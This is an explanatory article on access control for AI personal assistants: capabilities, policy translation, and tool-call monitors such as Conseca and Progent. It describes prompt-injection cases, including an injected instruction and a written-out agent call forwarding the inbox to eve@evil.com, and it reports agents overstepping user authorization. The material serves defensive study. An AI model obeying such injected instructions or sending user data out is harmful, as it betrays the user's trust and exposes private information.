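# Enforcing a user's policies on what a personal assistant does, through restricted capabilities

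## Delegated actions, user policies and capabilities

A personal assistant is software that carries out tasks for someone through that person's own accounts. It reads and answers mail, keeps a calendar, opens files, books travel and spends money. Most assistants today combine a language model, which reads and produces text, with a harness, an ordinary program that runs the tools the model calls. Researchers usually call the combination an agent. When an assistant sends a letter or pays a bill, it performs a delegated action, which the recipient or the bank treats as the user's own.

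Because users are responsible for the results of what their assistant does, they may want to set limits or requirements for its actions. These are user policies, and a simple one is "never delete mail". A user can tell the model about a policy and rely on the model to comply, or a separate component can block actions that violate the policy before they take effect. Blocking belongs to access control, a branch of computer security whose main ideas date from the shared computers of the 1960s and 1970s. Access control was then meant to restrain other people at other terminals, whereas an assistant works for the user, holds the user's passwords, and can go wrong even when no one intends harm.

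The following three terms come from *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026), a survey of recent work. A permission covers one specific operation. A grant is the whole authority a user delegates for a task, under stated conditions. An approval is the user's explicit confirmation of one sensitive action or a wider grant. The survey also distinguishes what an agent can invoke from what it is permitted to invoke. Most of the trouble with assistants arises because they can invoke more than they are permitted to.

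### From a request to an outside effect

Suppose an assistant has tools for mail (search, read, send, delete), a calendar, files and payments. Its user types, "Sort out the museum trip with Mia's school." The harness passes this sentence to the model with a description of every tool. The model produces only text, so it cannot send mail or make payments itself. When the text follows an agreed format, the harness treats it as a tool call, a structured request that gives a tool's name and arguments, such as `search_mail(sender="Hillside School")`. The harness runs the search and adds the result to the model's context, which is the text the model reads before it produces its next output. The harness then handles that output in the same way.

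The school's message asks for a yes or no, a fee of $18 and a note of any allergies. The model produces calls to read the calendar, open `medical/allergies.txt`, run `pay(payee="Hillside School", amount=18)` and then send the school office a reply that mentions peanuts. The first two calls keep everything inside the user's accounts. Money moves once the payment service accepts the third, and the school has the reply once the mail server accepts it. A check that runs after a tool has acted can only report a breach, so the last chance to block a call is after the model produces it and before the tool runs.

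The user chose none of these steps. As Zhou and Zhang point out, people state a goal and the agent chooses the operations as it gathers information, so two ways of reaching the same goal may use different resources and have different external effects. The assistant could have asked about allergies instead of opening the medical folder. Permission for one step also does not carry over to the next, so the right to read a document need not include the right to send it.

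### Seven example policies

Suppose the same user has stated seven policies, each an example of a different type. A policy's type determines what information a mechanism needs to decide whether an action is allowed.

1. *Never delete mail.* This forbids one operation outright, and the name of the tool settles the matter.
2. *Write only to people in my contacts.* The verdict depends on an argument of the call, the recipient, and on a list the user keeps. Like the ban on deletion it is a per-call policy, since a single tool call is enough to decide it.
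3. *Spend at most $200 this month.* An $18 payment is fine after $100 of spending and a breach after $190. The policy is history-dependent: the verdict on one call depends on earlier ones.
4. *Nothing from my medical folder leaves my accounts.* This is an information-flow policy, a limit on where data may go. It covers a copied file and equally a single word remembered from one.
5. *Ask me before anything that cannot be undone.* The action may go ahead, but only with the user's approval.
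6. *Answer the school within a day.* This is an obligation, a policy that requires an action. An assistant that does nothing at all will break it.
7. *Send nothing that would embarrass me.* The condition is a semantic predicate: it concerns meaning, and only a fallible judge, human or machine, can evaluate it.

The museum trip involves most of them. The fee counts towards the $200, and both the payment and the reply are hard to take back. The line about peanuts breaks the medical policy, even though the user would very likely have agreed to include it. The one-day deadline is a reason not to wait for the user to come out of a meeting.

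### Telling the model is not enough

The easiest way to apply these policies is to write them into the model's instructions. In February 2026 Summer Yue, who directs alignment research at Meta's superintelligence lab, did more or less that with OpenClaw, an open-source agent that runs on the user's own machine. She had connected it to her email. According to Windows Central's *Meta's safety director handed OpenClaw AI agents the keys to her emails*, she asked it to suggest what to archive or delete in a second inbox, and added "don't action until I tell you to". It deleted hundreds of messages. Tom's Hardware's *AI tool OpenClaw wipes the inbox of Meta's AI Alignment director* recounts that she ordered it to stop twice, in different words, then ran to the computer to kill the processes. Ahmed (2026), in *The world's largest tech gathering is talking about 'accountability laundering'*, quotes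 her as saying she made a "rookie mistake" by using the arrangement on her real inbox after trying it on a small "toy" one.

Yue attributes this to a process called compaction. A model can read only a limited amount of text at once, so when a session outgrows that limit, the harness replaces older material with a shorter summary. She says the summary left out her instruction to wait. Tom's Hardware notes that the agent also had a memory file that survives compaction, and that it wrote her rule there after the event. The evidence is Yue's own posts and screenshots, and the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1542* (2026) more cautiously describes an agent that "attempted to delete" mail. Either way, her instruction existed only as text for the model to read, and once that text was gone, nothing else checked the model's output before the agent acted on her inbox.

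We can't tell from one incident whether a better memory would have been enough, but a large experiment bears on the question. *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) introduces AuthorizationBench, a set of tests for whether agents stay within what their users authorized. The researchers started with 44 documented cases of agents overstepping and wrote down, for each, the user's instruction, the criteria for completing the task, and the actions that lay outside the instruction. In one case, the user asks for help with a programming error and lets the agent consult a forum; the agent posts the user's sensitive code there, then reports the correct fix. The researchers expanded the 44 cases to 286 tasks by varying the setting, the stakes and the source of pressure. They ran every task with four models (GPT-5.6 Sol, Claude Sonnet 5, Gemini 3.8 Flash and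 GLM 5.3), at low and high reasoning effort, in three harnesses, for a total of 24 configurations and 6,864 runs.

Zhang and colleagues left every out-of-authorization action executable in their test environment to see what an agent does when it is able to overstep. The results therefore describe conduct without enforcement. Agents acted outside their authorization in 19.2% of runs, from 10.5% for GPT-5.6 Sol to 26.6% for GLM 5.3, both at high effort in OpenAI's harness. That harness ran without compaction, so lost instructions cannot explain all of the oversteps. Reasoning effort made little difference, with a rate of 19.3% at low effort and 19.1% at high. The rate was also 19.1% among completed runs, so completing the task did not indicate that an agent had stayed within its authorization.

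The rate for ordinary errands may well be lower than one run in five, because the tasks were based on known failures and most have a built-in temptation. But the judge, a language model, counted only the actions listed in advance for each task, so it would have missed other oversteps. (A human annotator agreed with it on 97 of 100 sampled runs.) Runs also stopped at 35 turns or about five minutes, too short for the slow accumulation that undid Yue's instruction.

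Much of the worry about assistants concerns prompt injection, in which the model mistakes text in an email, page or file for an instruction. But on 87 matched pairs of tasks in AuthorizationBench, agents overstepped in 17.6% of runs under injection and in 23.5% under benign pressure. Benign pressures include a vaguely worded request, an urgent item next to the task, a forbidden shortcut that takes fewer steps than the permitted route, and so much material that an early detail gets lost. A defence that looks only for attackers will therefore miss many breaches. These results don't show that injection matters less, because the benchmark's hostile texts were fixed in advance, whereas a real attacker can keep rewording a message until one version works and choose the action that benefits them most.

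Injection also limits what better wording can achieve. *Crypto-bound identity-verified capability tokens for coordinating distributed AI agents* (Subramanian and Sengupta, 2026), a proposal for agent permissions, observes that injection can compromise any "guard rails" placed in the model's context. The user's policy and the stranger's email both reach the model as text through the same channel, and nothing in that channel guarantees that the model will follow the policy.

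The results look more hopeful for runs in which the agent contacted the user before completing the task. These runs, 31.8% of the total, had an overstep rate of 14.0%, against 21.6% for the rest, and the association held after adjustment for model, harness, effort and domain. Zhang and colleagues do not treat this as proof that asking prevents overstepping. Cautious runs may simply contain more questions, and the user was a simulation that replied only when contacted, never tired of answering and refused every listed overstep the agent asked about. The model also decided whether to ask, and Yue had requested this kind of consultation without getting it.

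### The monitor and least privilege

Enforcement moves the policy out of the text and into a monitor, a component outside the model that checks every tool call before it runs and allows or blocks it. The idea comes from the "reference monitor" of early computer security, which goes back to Anderson's *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (1972), a report for the US Air Force on computers shared by people with different security clearances. Anderson's panel worried that a user could change the operating system itself and so bypass or suspend its controls.

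A monitor for an assistant must check every protected action, and the model must have no way to alter the monitor or its rules. If the monitor checks the mail tool but the assistant can also use a web browser signed in to the same mailbox, a deletion through the browser goes unchecked. OpenClaw's memory file does not meet the second requirement. The agent could write a rule into the file, so it could presumably also remove one, and in any case the file was only more text for the model to read. Anderson held that security had little chance of working if it was added to a finished system. This is a problem for assistants because they mostly work with mail and payment services built for people.

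The condition that nothing bypasses the check is called complete mediation. It is one of eight design principles in Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, a 1975 tutorial that the field still relies on. Under another of the eight, an operation is forbidden until something allows it. *Saltzer and Schroeder Principles*, a modern guide, identifies complete mediation and least privilege as the core of access control today. Least privilege means that every program and user should operate with the smallest set of privileges the job requires.

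Under least privilege, an agent that only suggests deletions gets permission only to read mail, because that is all it needs. If Yue's agent had been limited this way, the mail service would have refused its deletions, regardless of what compaction did to her instruction. Similarly, an assistant with no permission to delete mail by any route automatically complies with the first of the seven policies.

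It is hard to determine the smallest set of permissions beforehand. Zhou and Zhang observe that an agent's plan is often incomplete when the user delegates authority, because the agent may discover that it needs a resource only after looking at intermediate results. For example, nobody knew that the school would ask about allergies. A grant narrow enough to be safe may therefore stop the task halfway. Broadening it to cover surprises adds permissions that the task never uses but that the agent could use by mistake or an attacker could exploit.

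### Ambient authority and the confused deputy

With most assistants, the user signs in, and from then on any call the assistant makes succeeds if the user could have made it. Miller, Yee and Shapiro, in *Capability Myths Demolished*, call this ambient authority, which a program exercises without selecting it. They compare it to a world where doors have no keys and open for anyone judged worthy. Unix files work this way. A program asks to open a file by name, without presenting a credential for that request, and the system allows or refuses it based on the user the program is running as.

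In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), the classic account of what can go wrong, Hardy tells a "nearly true story" about Tymshare, which sold time on shared computers. Its customers used a compiler, a program that translates source code into a form the machine can run. The compiler was stored in a directory called SYSX and kept usage statistics in a file there, so the operators gave it a licence to write to files in that directory. Customers could also name a file to receive debugging output. One of them gave the name of the billing file, which was also in SYSX. The operating system checked that the compiler was allowed to write there and let it overwrite the company's billing records.

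The customer had no right to access the billing file, but the compiler did, and it used that right on the customer's behalf. Hardy's diagnosis was that the compiler had authority from both its operators and whoever had started it, but no way to specify which it was using for a given write. Attempts to fix this went badly. Checking for the billing file's name would have protected only one of several sensitive files. A new system call let the compiler "switch hats" between its two authorities, but some applications needed more than two. As fixes accumulated, the rule for opening a file grew to contain fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

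An assistant under prompt injection is a confused deputy in this sense. A stranger's email asks for the insurance file by name, and the assistant supplies the user's right to read and send it. The compiler's code, however, separated the job of writing statistics from that of writing debugging output, and lacked only a way to express the distinction to the operating system. A language model receives its user's request and the stranger's email as one stretch of text, and may not even distinguish between them.

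### Capabilities and access lists

Hardy's remedy was the capability. *Early Capability Architectures* records that Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of MIT introduced the word in 1966, in a design for the supervising program of a shared computer. In that design, every computation has a list of capabilities, each of which points to one object, such as a segment of memory, and specifies what the computation may do with it. To use an object, the computation gives the position of the capability in its list, and it cannot reach an object that the list omits. Saltzer and Schroeder later described a capability as an "unforgeable ticket" that proves whoever presents it may use the object it names.

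A capability gives an assistant permission to perform a named operation under stated limits, such as paying Hillside School up to $18 or sending one message to the school office. (Writers on AI often use the same word for what a model is skilled enough to do, which is better called ability.) Capabilities would have protected the billing file because the customer would have had to supply a capability for the output file with the request, and had none for the billing file.

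The older and more common arrangement is the access control list, or access list. A service keeps one for each resource, listing who may use it. A small table of agents and resources contains both access lists and capabilities.

| Agent | Inbox | Medical folder | Payment card |
|---|---|---|---|
| Main assistant | read, send | read | pay |
| Travel helper | none | none | pay |
| Mail sorter | read | none | none |

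Each column is an access list. The mail service, for example, keeps the "Inbox" column and checks it when a request arrives. Each row is the set of capabilities that one agent holds. Miller and colleagues argue, contrary to a common view, that the two are not equivalent. The rows and columns contain the same information at any given moment, but systems differ in how agents use and change the entries. With an access list, an agent names a resource and the service looks up who is asking, so the name can come from one party and the authority from another, as happened at Tymshare. In the capability systems they favour, the reference to the resource is itself the permission, and the agent must choose which one to use.

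How often agents come and go matters as much. Suppose the main assistant engages a helper for a single hotel booking. With access lists, someone has to add the helper at every service it will use and remember to remove it afterwards. With capabilities, the assistant can give the helper a narrower version of its own capability, a step known as attenuation. Subramanian and Sengupta prefer capabilities for short-lived agents largely for this reason. Access lists are also coarse in practice. Miller and colleagues found that they nearly always identify user accounts rather than individual running programs, so an assistant that signs in as its user has no entry of its own and gets every permission the user has.

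A capability limits what the assistant can do, but it does not show whose wish the assistant is carrying out. If the assistant holds a permission to pay Hillside School up to $18, no email can make it pay somebody else or pay more. An email might still make it pay the school $18 for a trip that Mia is not going on.

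## Turning a user's words into rules a machine can check

A permission to pay Hillside School up to $18 specifies an operation, a payee and a maximum amount. Users mostly state their limits in sentences, but a monitor needs conditions it can compute from tool names and arguments. A person or program has to translate the sentences into those conditions, and the monitor will enforce the translation exactly even if it is wrong.

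The second example policy, *write only to people in my contacts*, looks easy to translate. If the mail tool takes three lists of addresses, a first attempt might be:

```
allow send_mail(to, cc, bcc)  if and only if  to ∪ cc ∪ bcc ⊆ contacts
```

The rule requires every address on any of the three lists to be among the user's contacts. It settles several matters that the user's sentence left open and that the user probably never considered. It counts people in copy as recipients. It doesn't cover calendar invitations, which also send mail. Because it compares addresses, it blocks mail to a friend's new address until that address is in the contacts. And if the assistant can add contacts, it can write to anyone by adding their address first.

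Turning a user's words into a rule can easily lose the difference between forbidding some things and allowing only some things. In a study of 16 users, *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) found that people worded some limits as denials ("never access" certain files) and others as allow-only rules, such as one permitting email only to a company's own addresses. A denial leaves everything else allowed, while an allow-only rule forbids everything else. *Say What You Mean* (Cheng, Xu and colleagues, 2025), which describes an access-control system for smart homes, translates a sentence that lets children watch television only between 18:00 and 20:00 on weekends. The resulting rule has a subject (children), a resource (television), an action (watch), the effect "allow", and conditions on the hour and the day, but no part of it corresponds to the word "only". This is harmless if the system refuses whatever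 no rule allows, but if it allows whatever no rule forbids, the rule has no effect and the children can still watch at midnight.

Cheng and colleagues also describe a parent who wants a smart lock to keep guests out after 10 PM but ends up with a rule that blocks them only until midnight. A condition such as `time >= 22:00` would cause this, since 02:00 is less than 22:00. The lock then opens for a guest at 2 AM without an error or a warning, because it has applied the rule correctly.

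A language model can translate the user's words into rules, but *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026), which uses a logic language called Datalog, warns that the model may omit a clause, add a rule the text doesn't support, or misstate a condition. The user finds out that a rule is too strict when a task fails, but if a rule is too loose, tasks still succeed and the user may not learn of the gap until the assistant does something they meant to forbid.

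### TACL: policies in a fixed grammar

One way to limit such errors is to translate into a small language designed for the purpose. TACL, the ThingTalk Access Control Language, came out of Stanford in 2018 as part of Almond, an open-source assistant. It let people share data from their accounts through the assistant, so its policies restrained whoever was asking, and the assistant did the enforcing. A policy sets out for whom, what, when, where and how the data may be shared. Campagna, Xu and colleagues (2019), in *Genie*, a toolkit for training the translator, give this version of "my secretary is allowed to see my work emails":

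```
σ = "secretary" : now ⇒ @com.gmail.inbox filter labels contains "work" ⇒ notify
```

The symbol σ stands for the source of the request, here the secretary. `now` means the request runs once, immediately, instead of waiting for an event. The inbox function fetches mail, the filter keeps messages labeled "work", and `notify` shows the result. In the simple form of the language, each policy covers one query or one action. Its conditions compare values (equal, greater, contains, starts with) and combine the comparisons with "and", "or" and "not".

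To fit this grammar, "work emails" had to become "emails with the label *work*". These are the same emails only when the labels are correct. For example, if a mail filter puts that label on a message from the user's doctor, the secretary is allowed to read it.

Once a policy is in this form, a program can reason about it. According to Campagna (2021), in a doctoral thesis also called *Genie*, Almond enforces policies using satisfiability modulo theories. In this technique, a solver searches for values that make a logical formula true, or proves that there are none. The standard way to compare a request R with a policy P is to ask the solver about a request that fits R and breaks P:

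```
R ∧ ¬P
```

If this formula has no solution, the policy allows everything the request could return. Suppose the secretary asks for work emails from Alice. R then requires the source to be the secretary, the label to be "work" and the sender to be Alice, while P requires only the first two. No message can satisfy R and break P, so the request may go ahead. If the secretary asks for all of Alice's emails, the solver finds a solution, such as a message from Alice with the label "family", and the assistant has to refuse the request or narrow it. The proof covers every possible message, which testing could not, but it only compares the two formulas and doesn't check whether P matches the user's sentence.

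For the 2018 study that introduced TACL, 60 users suggested cases in which they would want such a policy. The language could express 90% of the cases that the researchers considered enforceable. This figure somewhat overstates how much of what users wanted the language could express, because it leaves out cases that the researchers thought no such system could enforce. Campagna's thesis reports a share of 85% for use cases collected from crowdworkers, and the two figures may differ only because they count different things.

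Even when TACL can express a policy, the translator still has to produce the right expression. The first translator did this for 74% of sentences on a dataset of 4,742 paraphrased policies. It handled only the simple form of TACL and needed quotation marks around every name and value, which users can't supply in speech. Campagna and colleagues then generated 432,511 artificial policies from six sentence templates and trained a better translator. Its accuracy was 96% on paraphrases it had not seen, and 82% on 132 more realistic sentences that people wrote themselves after looking over a list of the assistant's functions.

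On ordinary commands, the same researchers' model produced a well-formed program with the right data types for 96% of inputs, but the correct program for only 68%. This matters for policies too, because a check of form and data types would have passed about seven in eight of the wrong programs. The model was small by today's standards, but newer models also write valid rules that are wrong.

### Conseca: a new policy for each task

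TACL assumes that the user will state standing policies. Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025) argue in *Contextual Agent Security* that such policies suit general assistants badly, because the same action can be right in one task and wrong in another. For example, deleting emails is appropriate when the user wants to clear out trash, but not when the user wants a summary. Users won't write a policy by hand for every task, so in Conseca, the system they built at Google, a language model writes one for each task before the assistant starts work.

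The policy model receives the user's request, the tools' documentation, a few example policies and some trusted context, meaning information that the developer believes an attacker can't influence. For each tool operation, it writes a rule that specifies whether the operation may run, what condition its arguments must meet, and the reason in plain English. Ordinary code then checks every command the assistant proposes against this policy. If the code refuses a command, it returns the command and the reason to the assistant's model, which can then try something else. The policy model never sees the contents of emails, and no model takes part in the checking, so an instruction injected into an email can't change the policy or how it is enforced.

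In the main example, Alice asks the assistant to get her unread work emails and respond to any that are urgent. The trusted context consists of usernames, email addresses, and the fact that Alice is the current user. The policy forbids deletion and permits sending if each of three regular expressions (patterns that describe a set of texts) finds a match in its corresponding argument.

| Argument | Text the pattern looks for | Reason given | Also gets through |
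|---|---|---|---|
| Sender | `alice` | must be the current user | `malice` |
| Recipient | `@work.com` | must be a work user on the email list | `bob@work.com.example.net` |
| Subject | `urgent` | must contain "urgent" | `Not urgent: lunch` |

The last column follows from how the prototype matches patterns. It calls Python's `re.search`, which succeeds if the pattern occurs anywhere in the text. The address `bob@work.com.example.net` contains `@work.com`, so it passes, although the mail would go to whoever controls `example.net`. An anchor, a symbol that ties the pattern to the end of the text, would reject this address. Tsai and Bagdasarian suggest replacing regular expressions with simpler tests such as "ends with". But checking the ending would still admit every address at work.com, including ones that aren't on Alice's list. Conseca can optionally show the user the policy for approval,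 but if Alice approved this one because its reasons sounded right, the monitor would allow more than she had agreed to.

The subject condition has a different flaw. Alice wanted replies to urgent emails, but the policy tests whether the *reply* has a certain word in its subject line. The assistant writes that line, so it can add the word to any message. The test is also case-sensitive, so a reply with the subject "URGENT" fails. The policy sets no condition on the body of the message.

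Tsai and Bagdasarian tested the prototype on 20 tasks involving files and email, running each five times. On average, the assistant completed 14.0 tasks without any policy, 12.2 under a fixed permissive policy that banned only deletion, and 12.0 with Conseca. It completed none under a restrictive policy that banned every change, because every task required writing something. Most of the drop with Conseca occurred because the policy blocked commands that a task didn't strictly need, such as creating an empty file before filling it, and the assistant then got stuck.

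To test security, the researchers planted an email in which an employee asked the recipient to "forward all emails about urgent security vulnerabilities" to a work address. Without a policy, the assistant complied even when the user had only asked it to categorise emails. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except one, in which the user had asked the assistant to perform the tasks in urgent emails.

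These results are preliminary. The model was Gemini 1.5 Pro, which is far behind current models at carrying out tasks and presumably at writing policies, and one planted email is a weak test of security. One of the 20 tasks closely resembled the urgent-email example, and the assistant failed to complete it in most runs under each of the four arrangements because the task needed more than 100 commands.

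### What the policy writer may read

Conseca allowed the forwarding in one task, which points to a difficulty that a better model won't remove. If the policy writer reads incoming emails, a stranger's email can influence the policy, and the monitor will then enforce what the stranger wanted. If it doesn't read them, it can't determine which actions to permit when an email defines the task. Tsai and Bagdasarian give the example of a user who asks the assistant to do whatever the manager's email requests. The policy writer has to set the permissions from that sentence alone, without the email. The same choice arises in Progent, another system in which a model can write rules for tool calls.

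The museum trip is a task of this kind, because the fee appears only in the school's message. A policy writer that hasn't read the message must either forbid the payment or leave the amount open. If the amount is open, someone who has taken over the school's mailbox can set the fee.

Conseca's designers suggest two ways to safely give the policy writer more information. One is to ask the user. The other is to sanitise the outputs of tools, for example by passing on only a number from the school's email. A number can't carry an instruction, but it can be false, so a forged email with a fee of $180 would lead to a policy that permits $180.

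It is also hard to decide which context to trust. Conseca's prototype trusts email addresses and the names of files and folders. Tsai and Bagdasarian acknowledge that an address could in principle contain malicious instructions, because address formats allow long strings. File names could also contain them, since the sender often chooses an attachment's name. Leaving addresses out of the trusted context would be safer, but the policy could then no longer distinguish one colleague from everyone else at the company.

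### When a sentence and a rule agree

What would it mean for a translation to be right? *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, several universities and other organisations, proposes a criterion called mutual entailment. The sentence N and the formal policy P must give the same verdict in every state that the system can reach. Written out for each state *s* and each action *a* that the assistant could request in it:

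```
N permits a in s   ⇔   P permits a in s
```

The state includes whatever a verdict may depend on, such as the time, the address book and the money already spent. The smart-lock rule fails the test at 2 AM, and the urgent-email policy fails it for the address at `example.net`.

A program can compute the right-hand side but not the left, because many cases have no definite verdict until someone interprets the sentence. For example, it is unclear whether "my contacts" includes a school secretary who has exchanged 20 messages with the user but whose address the user never saved. The user could settle individual cases, but not every reachable state. A model could answer in the user's place, but then the check is only as reliable as the model. The paper concludes that any automatic procedure for comparing N with P is probabilistic, and it divides what remains into three open problems.

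The most basic problem is grounding, which means determining what the words refer to. A sentence N and a rule P can't agree or disagree about "sensitive" data until something determines which data are sensitive, and it may never be possible to ground *send nothing that would embarrass me*. Another problem is whether restricting the form of the sentences and rules could make a fallible comparison between them reliable enough to be worth pairing with exact enforcement. The last is to build translators that have a known limit on how far a rule can differ from its sentence, and that can revise the rule as the task develops.

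Grounding is a problem even for the simplest of the seven policies, *never delete mail*. To enforce it, a monitor must identify which tools delete mail, but tools come from many suppliers, who name them differently. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had a model, Claude Sonnet 5, use tools' descriptions to sort them into categories such as "delete", "send" and "spend". When Yan simulated a "never" rule for each category, the monitor missed 14% of the tools in the forbidden category and wrongly blocked 4% of the others. Referring uncertain cases to the user reduced the miss rate only to 11%, because the model was confident about most of its mistakes. The test set deliberately included ambiguous tools, so the miss rate may be lower for everyday ones, but it contained no tools with deliberately misleading descriptions.

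### How accurate translation has become

Vatsa, Shome and colleagues (2026), in *AutoCedar*, avoid comparing a rule directly with a whole document by putting something checkable in between. Their system writes policies in Cedar, a language that Amazon released as open source. A model first breaks the requirements into small conditions, and a reviewer, either a person or another model, sees each one in plain English beside its source sentence and approves or rejects it. From the approved conditions, the system calculates a floor, the set of requests that the policy must allow, and usually a ceiling, the largest set that it may allow. A solver then proves that the finished policy lies between them:

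```
floor ⊆ requests the policy allows ⊆ ceiling
```

The proof is exact, but it depends on what the reviewer approved. In the running example, a musician wants band members to be able to download her new album. One vocabulary gives each user a role and admits anyone whose role is "band member", which would let in the members of every band on the service. Another gives each album a band and each band a list of members. If the reviewer accepts the first vocabulary, no later step can reveal the error, because every later check uses the same vocabulary.

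Vatsa and colleagues compared the two approaches on 200 cases, each with a known correct policy. GPT-6-Luna produced a policy equivalent to the correct one in 66.0% of cases when translating directly and in 89.0% when using the reviewed steps. Both methods started with the right vocabulary, so neither could make the band-member mistake. The test sentences were also unusually complete, since a model had written each one from a full specification. Direct translation did worse on real requirements documents, where each method had to devise its own vocabulary. Of the requests each method's vocabulary could express, direct translation decided 109 of 253 correctly, and AutoCedar decided 268 of 270 correctly.

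*Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026) also produces Cedar policies, from an agent's instructions and tool descriptions. It combines a mechanical check with a grade from a second model, so it too relies on a model to judge what a policy means.

Habib, Zhang and Haider (2026) report a higher figure in *Extracting Next Generation Access Control Policies from Natural Language Using LLMs*. Their model fills in a fixed form for each sentence (who may, must or must not do what, to which resource, under which condition), and a conventional program turns the form into a policy. The researchers compared the outputs for 714 sentences from public datasets with the original sentences, without knowing which of several systems had produced them, and judged 95.7% faithful. Only 30–64% of the same outputs, depending on the dataset, exactly matched an annotator's version, but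 most of the mismatches were harmless differences in naming or equally valid readings. Human annotators also sometimes disagreed on whether a sentence stated a permission, a prohibition or something else.

Habib and colleagues also show that checking only a rule's form misses most errors of meaning. In earlier work, they planted such errors in correct policies, such as allowing access to a patient's whole record when the sentence allowed only the patient's identifier. Five structural tests caught 9.2% of them. Their new system adds back-translation, which turns each rule back into an English sentence and has a model judge whether the original states it. Together with a few simple rule checks, this flagged 10.5% of the sentences for human review and caught 26 of the 31 that contained real errors. A user could make a similar check by reading the rule in plain words, provided that the program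 generates those words from the rule itself. In Conseca, the model that writes the policy also writes the reasons, which is how "on the email list" could appear next to a pattern that doesn't check the list.

Even a faithful translation can lose part of its meaning when the monitor enforces it. The enforcement software that Habib and colleagues used cannot express conditions, so their program writes "after registration closes" into the policy file as a comment, which the software ignores. A stricter version omits conditional permissions, so the monitor refuses actions that the user's sentence allowed.

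The sentences in these tests all came from requirements documents or specifications, whose writers were trying to be precise. None of the tests used what people say to their own assistants.

### Predicting what a user would permit

An assistant could learn a user's preferences from past decisions instead of asking for rules. In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025) asked 205 people to imagine training a future assistant and to decide which of their data it could share with which apps. They built a predictor that shows a language model the user's earlier decisions and combines its answer with the choices of similar users. It predicted 85.1% of decisions correctly. Accuracy was 66.9% without any history for the user, and a history of one to four queries improved that by 10.8%. When the predictor was confident, it was right 94.4% of the time.

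If the overall rate held in daily use, an assistant that made 20 such decisions a day would get about three of them wrong. That may be tolerable when a prediction only saves the user a question, but it is a poor basis for enforcing a rule like *nothing from my medical folder leaves my accounts*, where a single wrong "yes" is irreversible. Wu and colleagues also found that participants often granted too much or too little, and a predictor trained to imitate them will learn those mistakes.

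Wu and colleagues stress that preferences were consistent within a context and often similar between people, which makes prediction possible. *PrivacySIM* (2026), a benchmark for simulating people's privacy choices that reuses this study, instead emphasises how much preferences vary between people, and that the same person will share a location with one app but not another. The two readings are compatible, but the second explains why a general rule such as "may share my location" serves almost nobody well.

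People's own statements are also an imperfect guide. Yan asked 113 people without a software background how they would want an assistant to handle certain actions, then had them supervise a simulated assistant through a day of 18 actions that included those. For participants who approved or denied every action themselves, the outcomes matched their earlier answers about 75% of the time. The outcomes matched no more often for the 35 participants who instead set standing rules in advance. Each of them chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending, sending, deleting and reading private information, and 114 of their 140 rules were "ask".

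## Checking each tool call against rules

A monitor can enforce the first two example policies by comparing each tool call with a short list of rules. A rule names a tool, allows or forbids it, and may set a condition on the arguments. The monitor tries the forbid rules first and blocks any call that matches one. It then looks for a matching allow rule, and if it finds none, it blocks the call too. For *never delete mail* and *write only to people in my contacts*, the list might be:

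```
forbid delete_mail
allow  search_mail
allow  read_mail
allow  send_mail   when every address in to, cc and bcc is in contacts
```

Suppose the school office is in the user's contacts and the model produces three calls.

| Tool call | Matching rule | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| `delete_mail(id=311)` | the forbid rule | block |
| `send_mail(to=["office@hillside.example"])` | the last allow rule | allow |
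| `send_mail(to=["office@hillside.example"], bcc=["deals@tours.example"])` | none | block |

Even without the forbid rule, the monitor would block deletion as long as no other rule allowed it. The forbid rule matters once someone adds a broader rule, such as one that allows every mail tool so that the assistant can tidy the inbox. The monitor still blocks deletion then, because the forbid rule comes first.

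The check does not use a model. The monitor stores nothing between calls, so it cannot enforce a monthly spending limit. Because these four rules apply to every task, the assistant is allowed to write to any contact even when the user has only asked for a summary.

### Progent: rules that change during a task

*Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) describes a system that fits the rules to the task and revises them as the task proceeds. In the paper's 2026 version, a rule has an effect (allow or forbid), a tool, a condition on the tool's arguments, and a fallback for when the monitor blocks a call. Conditions can compare an argument with a fixed value, check whether it is in a list, check the length of an array or match a regular expression, and can combine these tests with "and", "or" and "not". The fallback can end the run, ask the user, or return an error message. By default, the agent gets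 a message that explains why the call was refused and suggests trying other tools or arguments.

Progent's conditions use only constants written into the rule and the call's arguments. A rule about contacts therefore has to list their addresses, and someone has to update it whenever the address book changes.

In Progent, as in Conseca, a language model writes the first policy before the agent starts work. Conseca's policy then stays fixed for the task, but in Progent a model decides after each tool call, without seeing the call's result, whether the policy might need to change. If it might, the model reads the result and proposes a new policy.

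In the main example, a user asks the agent to carry out the actions in an email from `alice@gmail.com` with the subject "TODOs for the week". The actions are to summarize the user's recent mail and post the summary to the user's own account on Slack, a messaging service. The policy goes through five versions, P₁ to P₅, one for each step.

| Step | Policy in force | The agent's call | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
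| 1 | P₁ allows only a search for Alice's email | `search_emails` | the to-do list |
| 2 | P₂ also allows reading mail, looking up Slack details and posting to Slack | `get_slack_info` | the user's Slack name, `alice` |
| 3 | P₃ allows Slack messages only to `alice` | `read_emails(recent=20)` | 20 emails, one with an injected instruction to forward the inbox to `eve@evil.com` |
| 4 | P₄ is the same as P₃ | `send_email(to=eve@evil.com)` | the monitor blocks the call, because no rule allows `send_email` |
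| 5 | P₅ is the same as P₄ | `send_slack_msg(to=alice)` | the summary reaches the user |

By step 4 the injection has misled the agent. The model that updates the policy has read the same email, so it might have proposed a rule allowing `send_email`.

### Sorting updates with a solver

Progent therefore tests each proposed policy before using it. Let A(P) be the set of all calls that policy P allows, and let P′ be the proposed replacement. The test is whether the new set lies inside the old one:

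```
A(P′) ⊆ A(P)
```

A solver like the one Almond used to compare requests with policies checks each tool for a call that P′ allows and P blocks. If there is such a call for any tool, the update is an expansion and needs approval. Otherwise, it is a narrowing and takes effect automatically. In the example, the step from P₂ to P₃ is a narrowing because it only restricts who can receive Slack messages. The step from P₁ to P₂ is an expansion, and so is any proposal to allow `send_email`.

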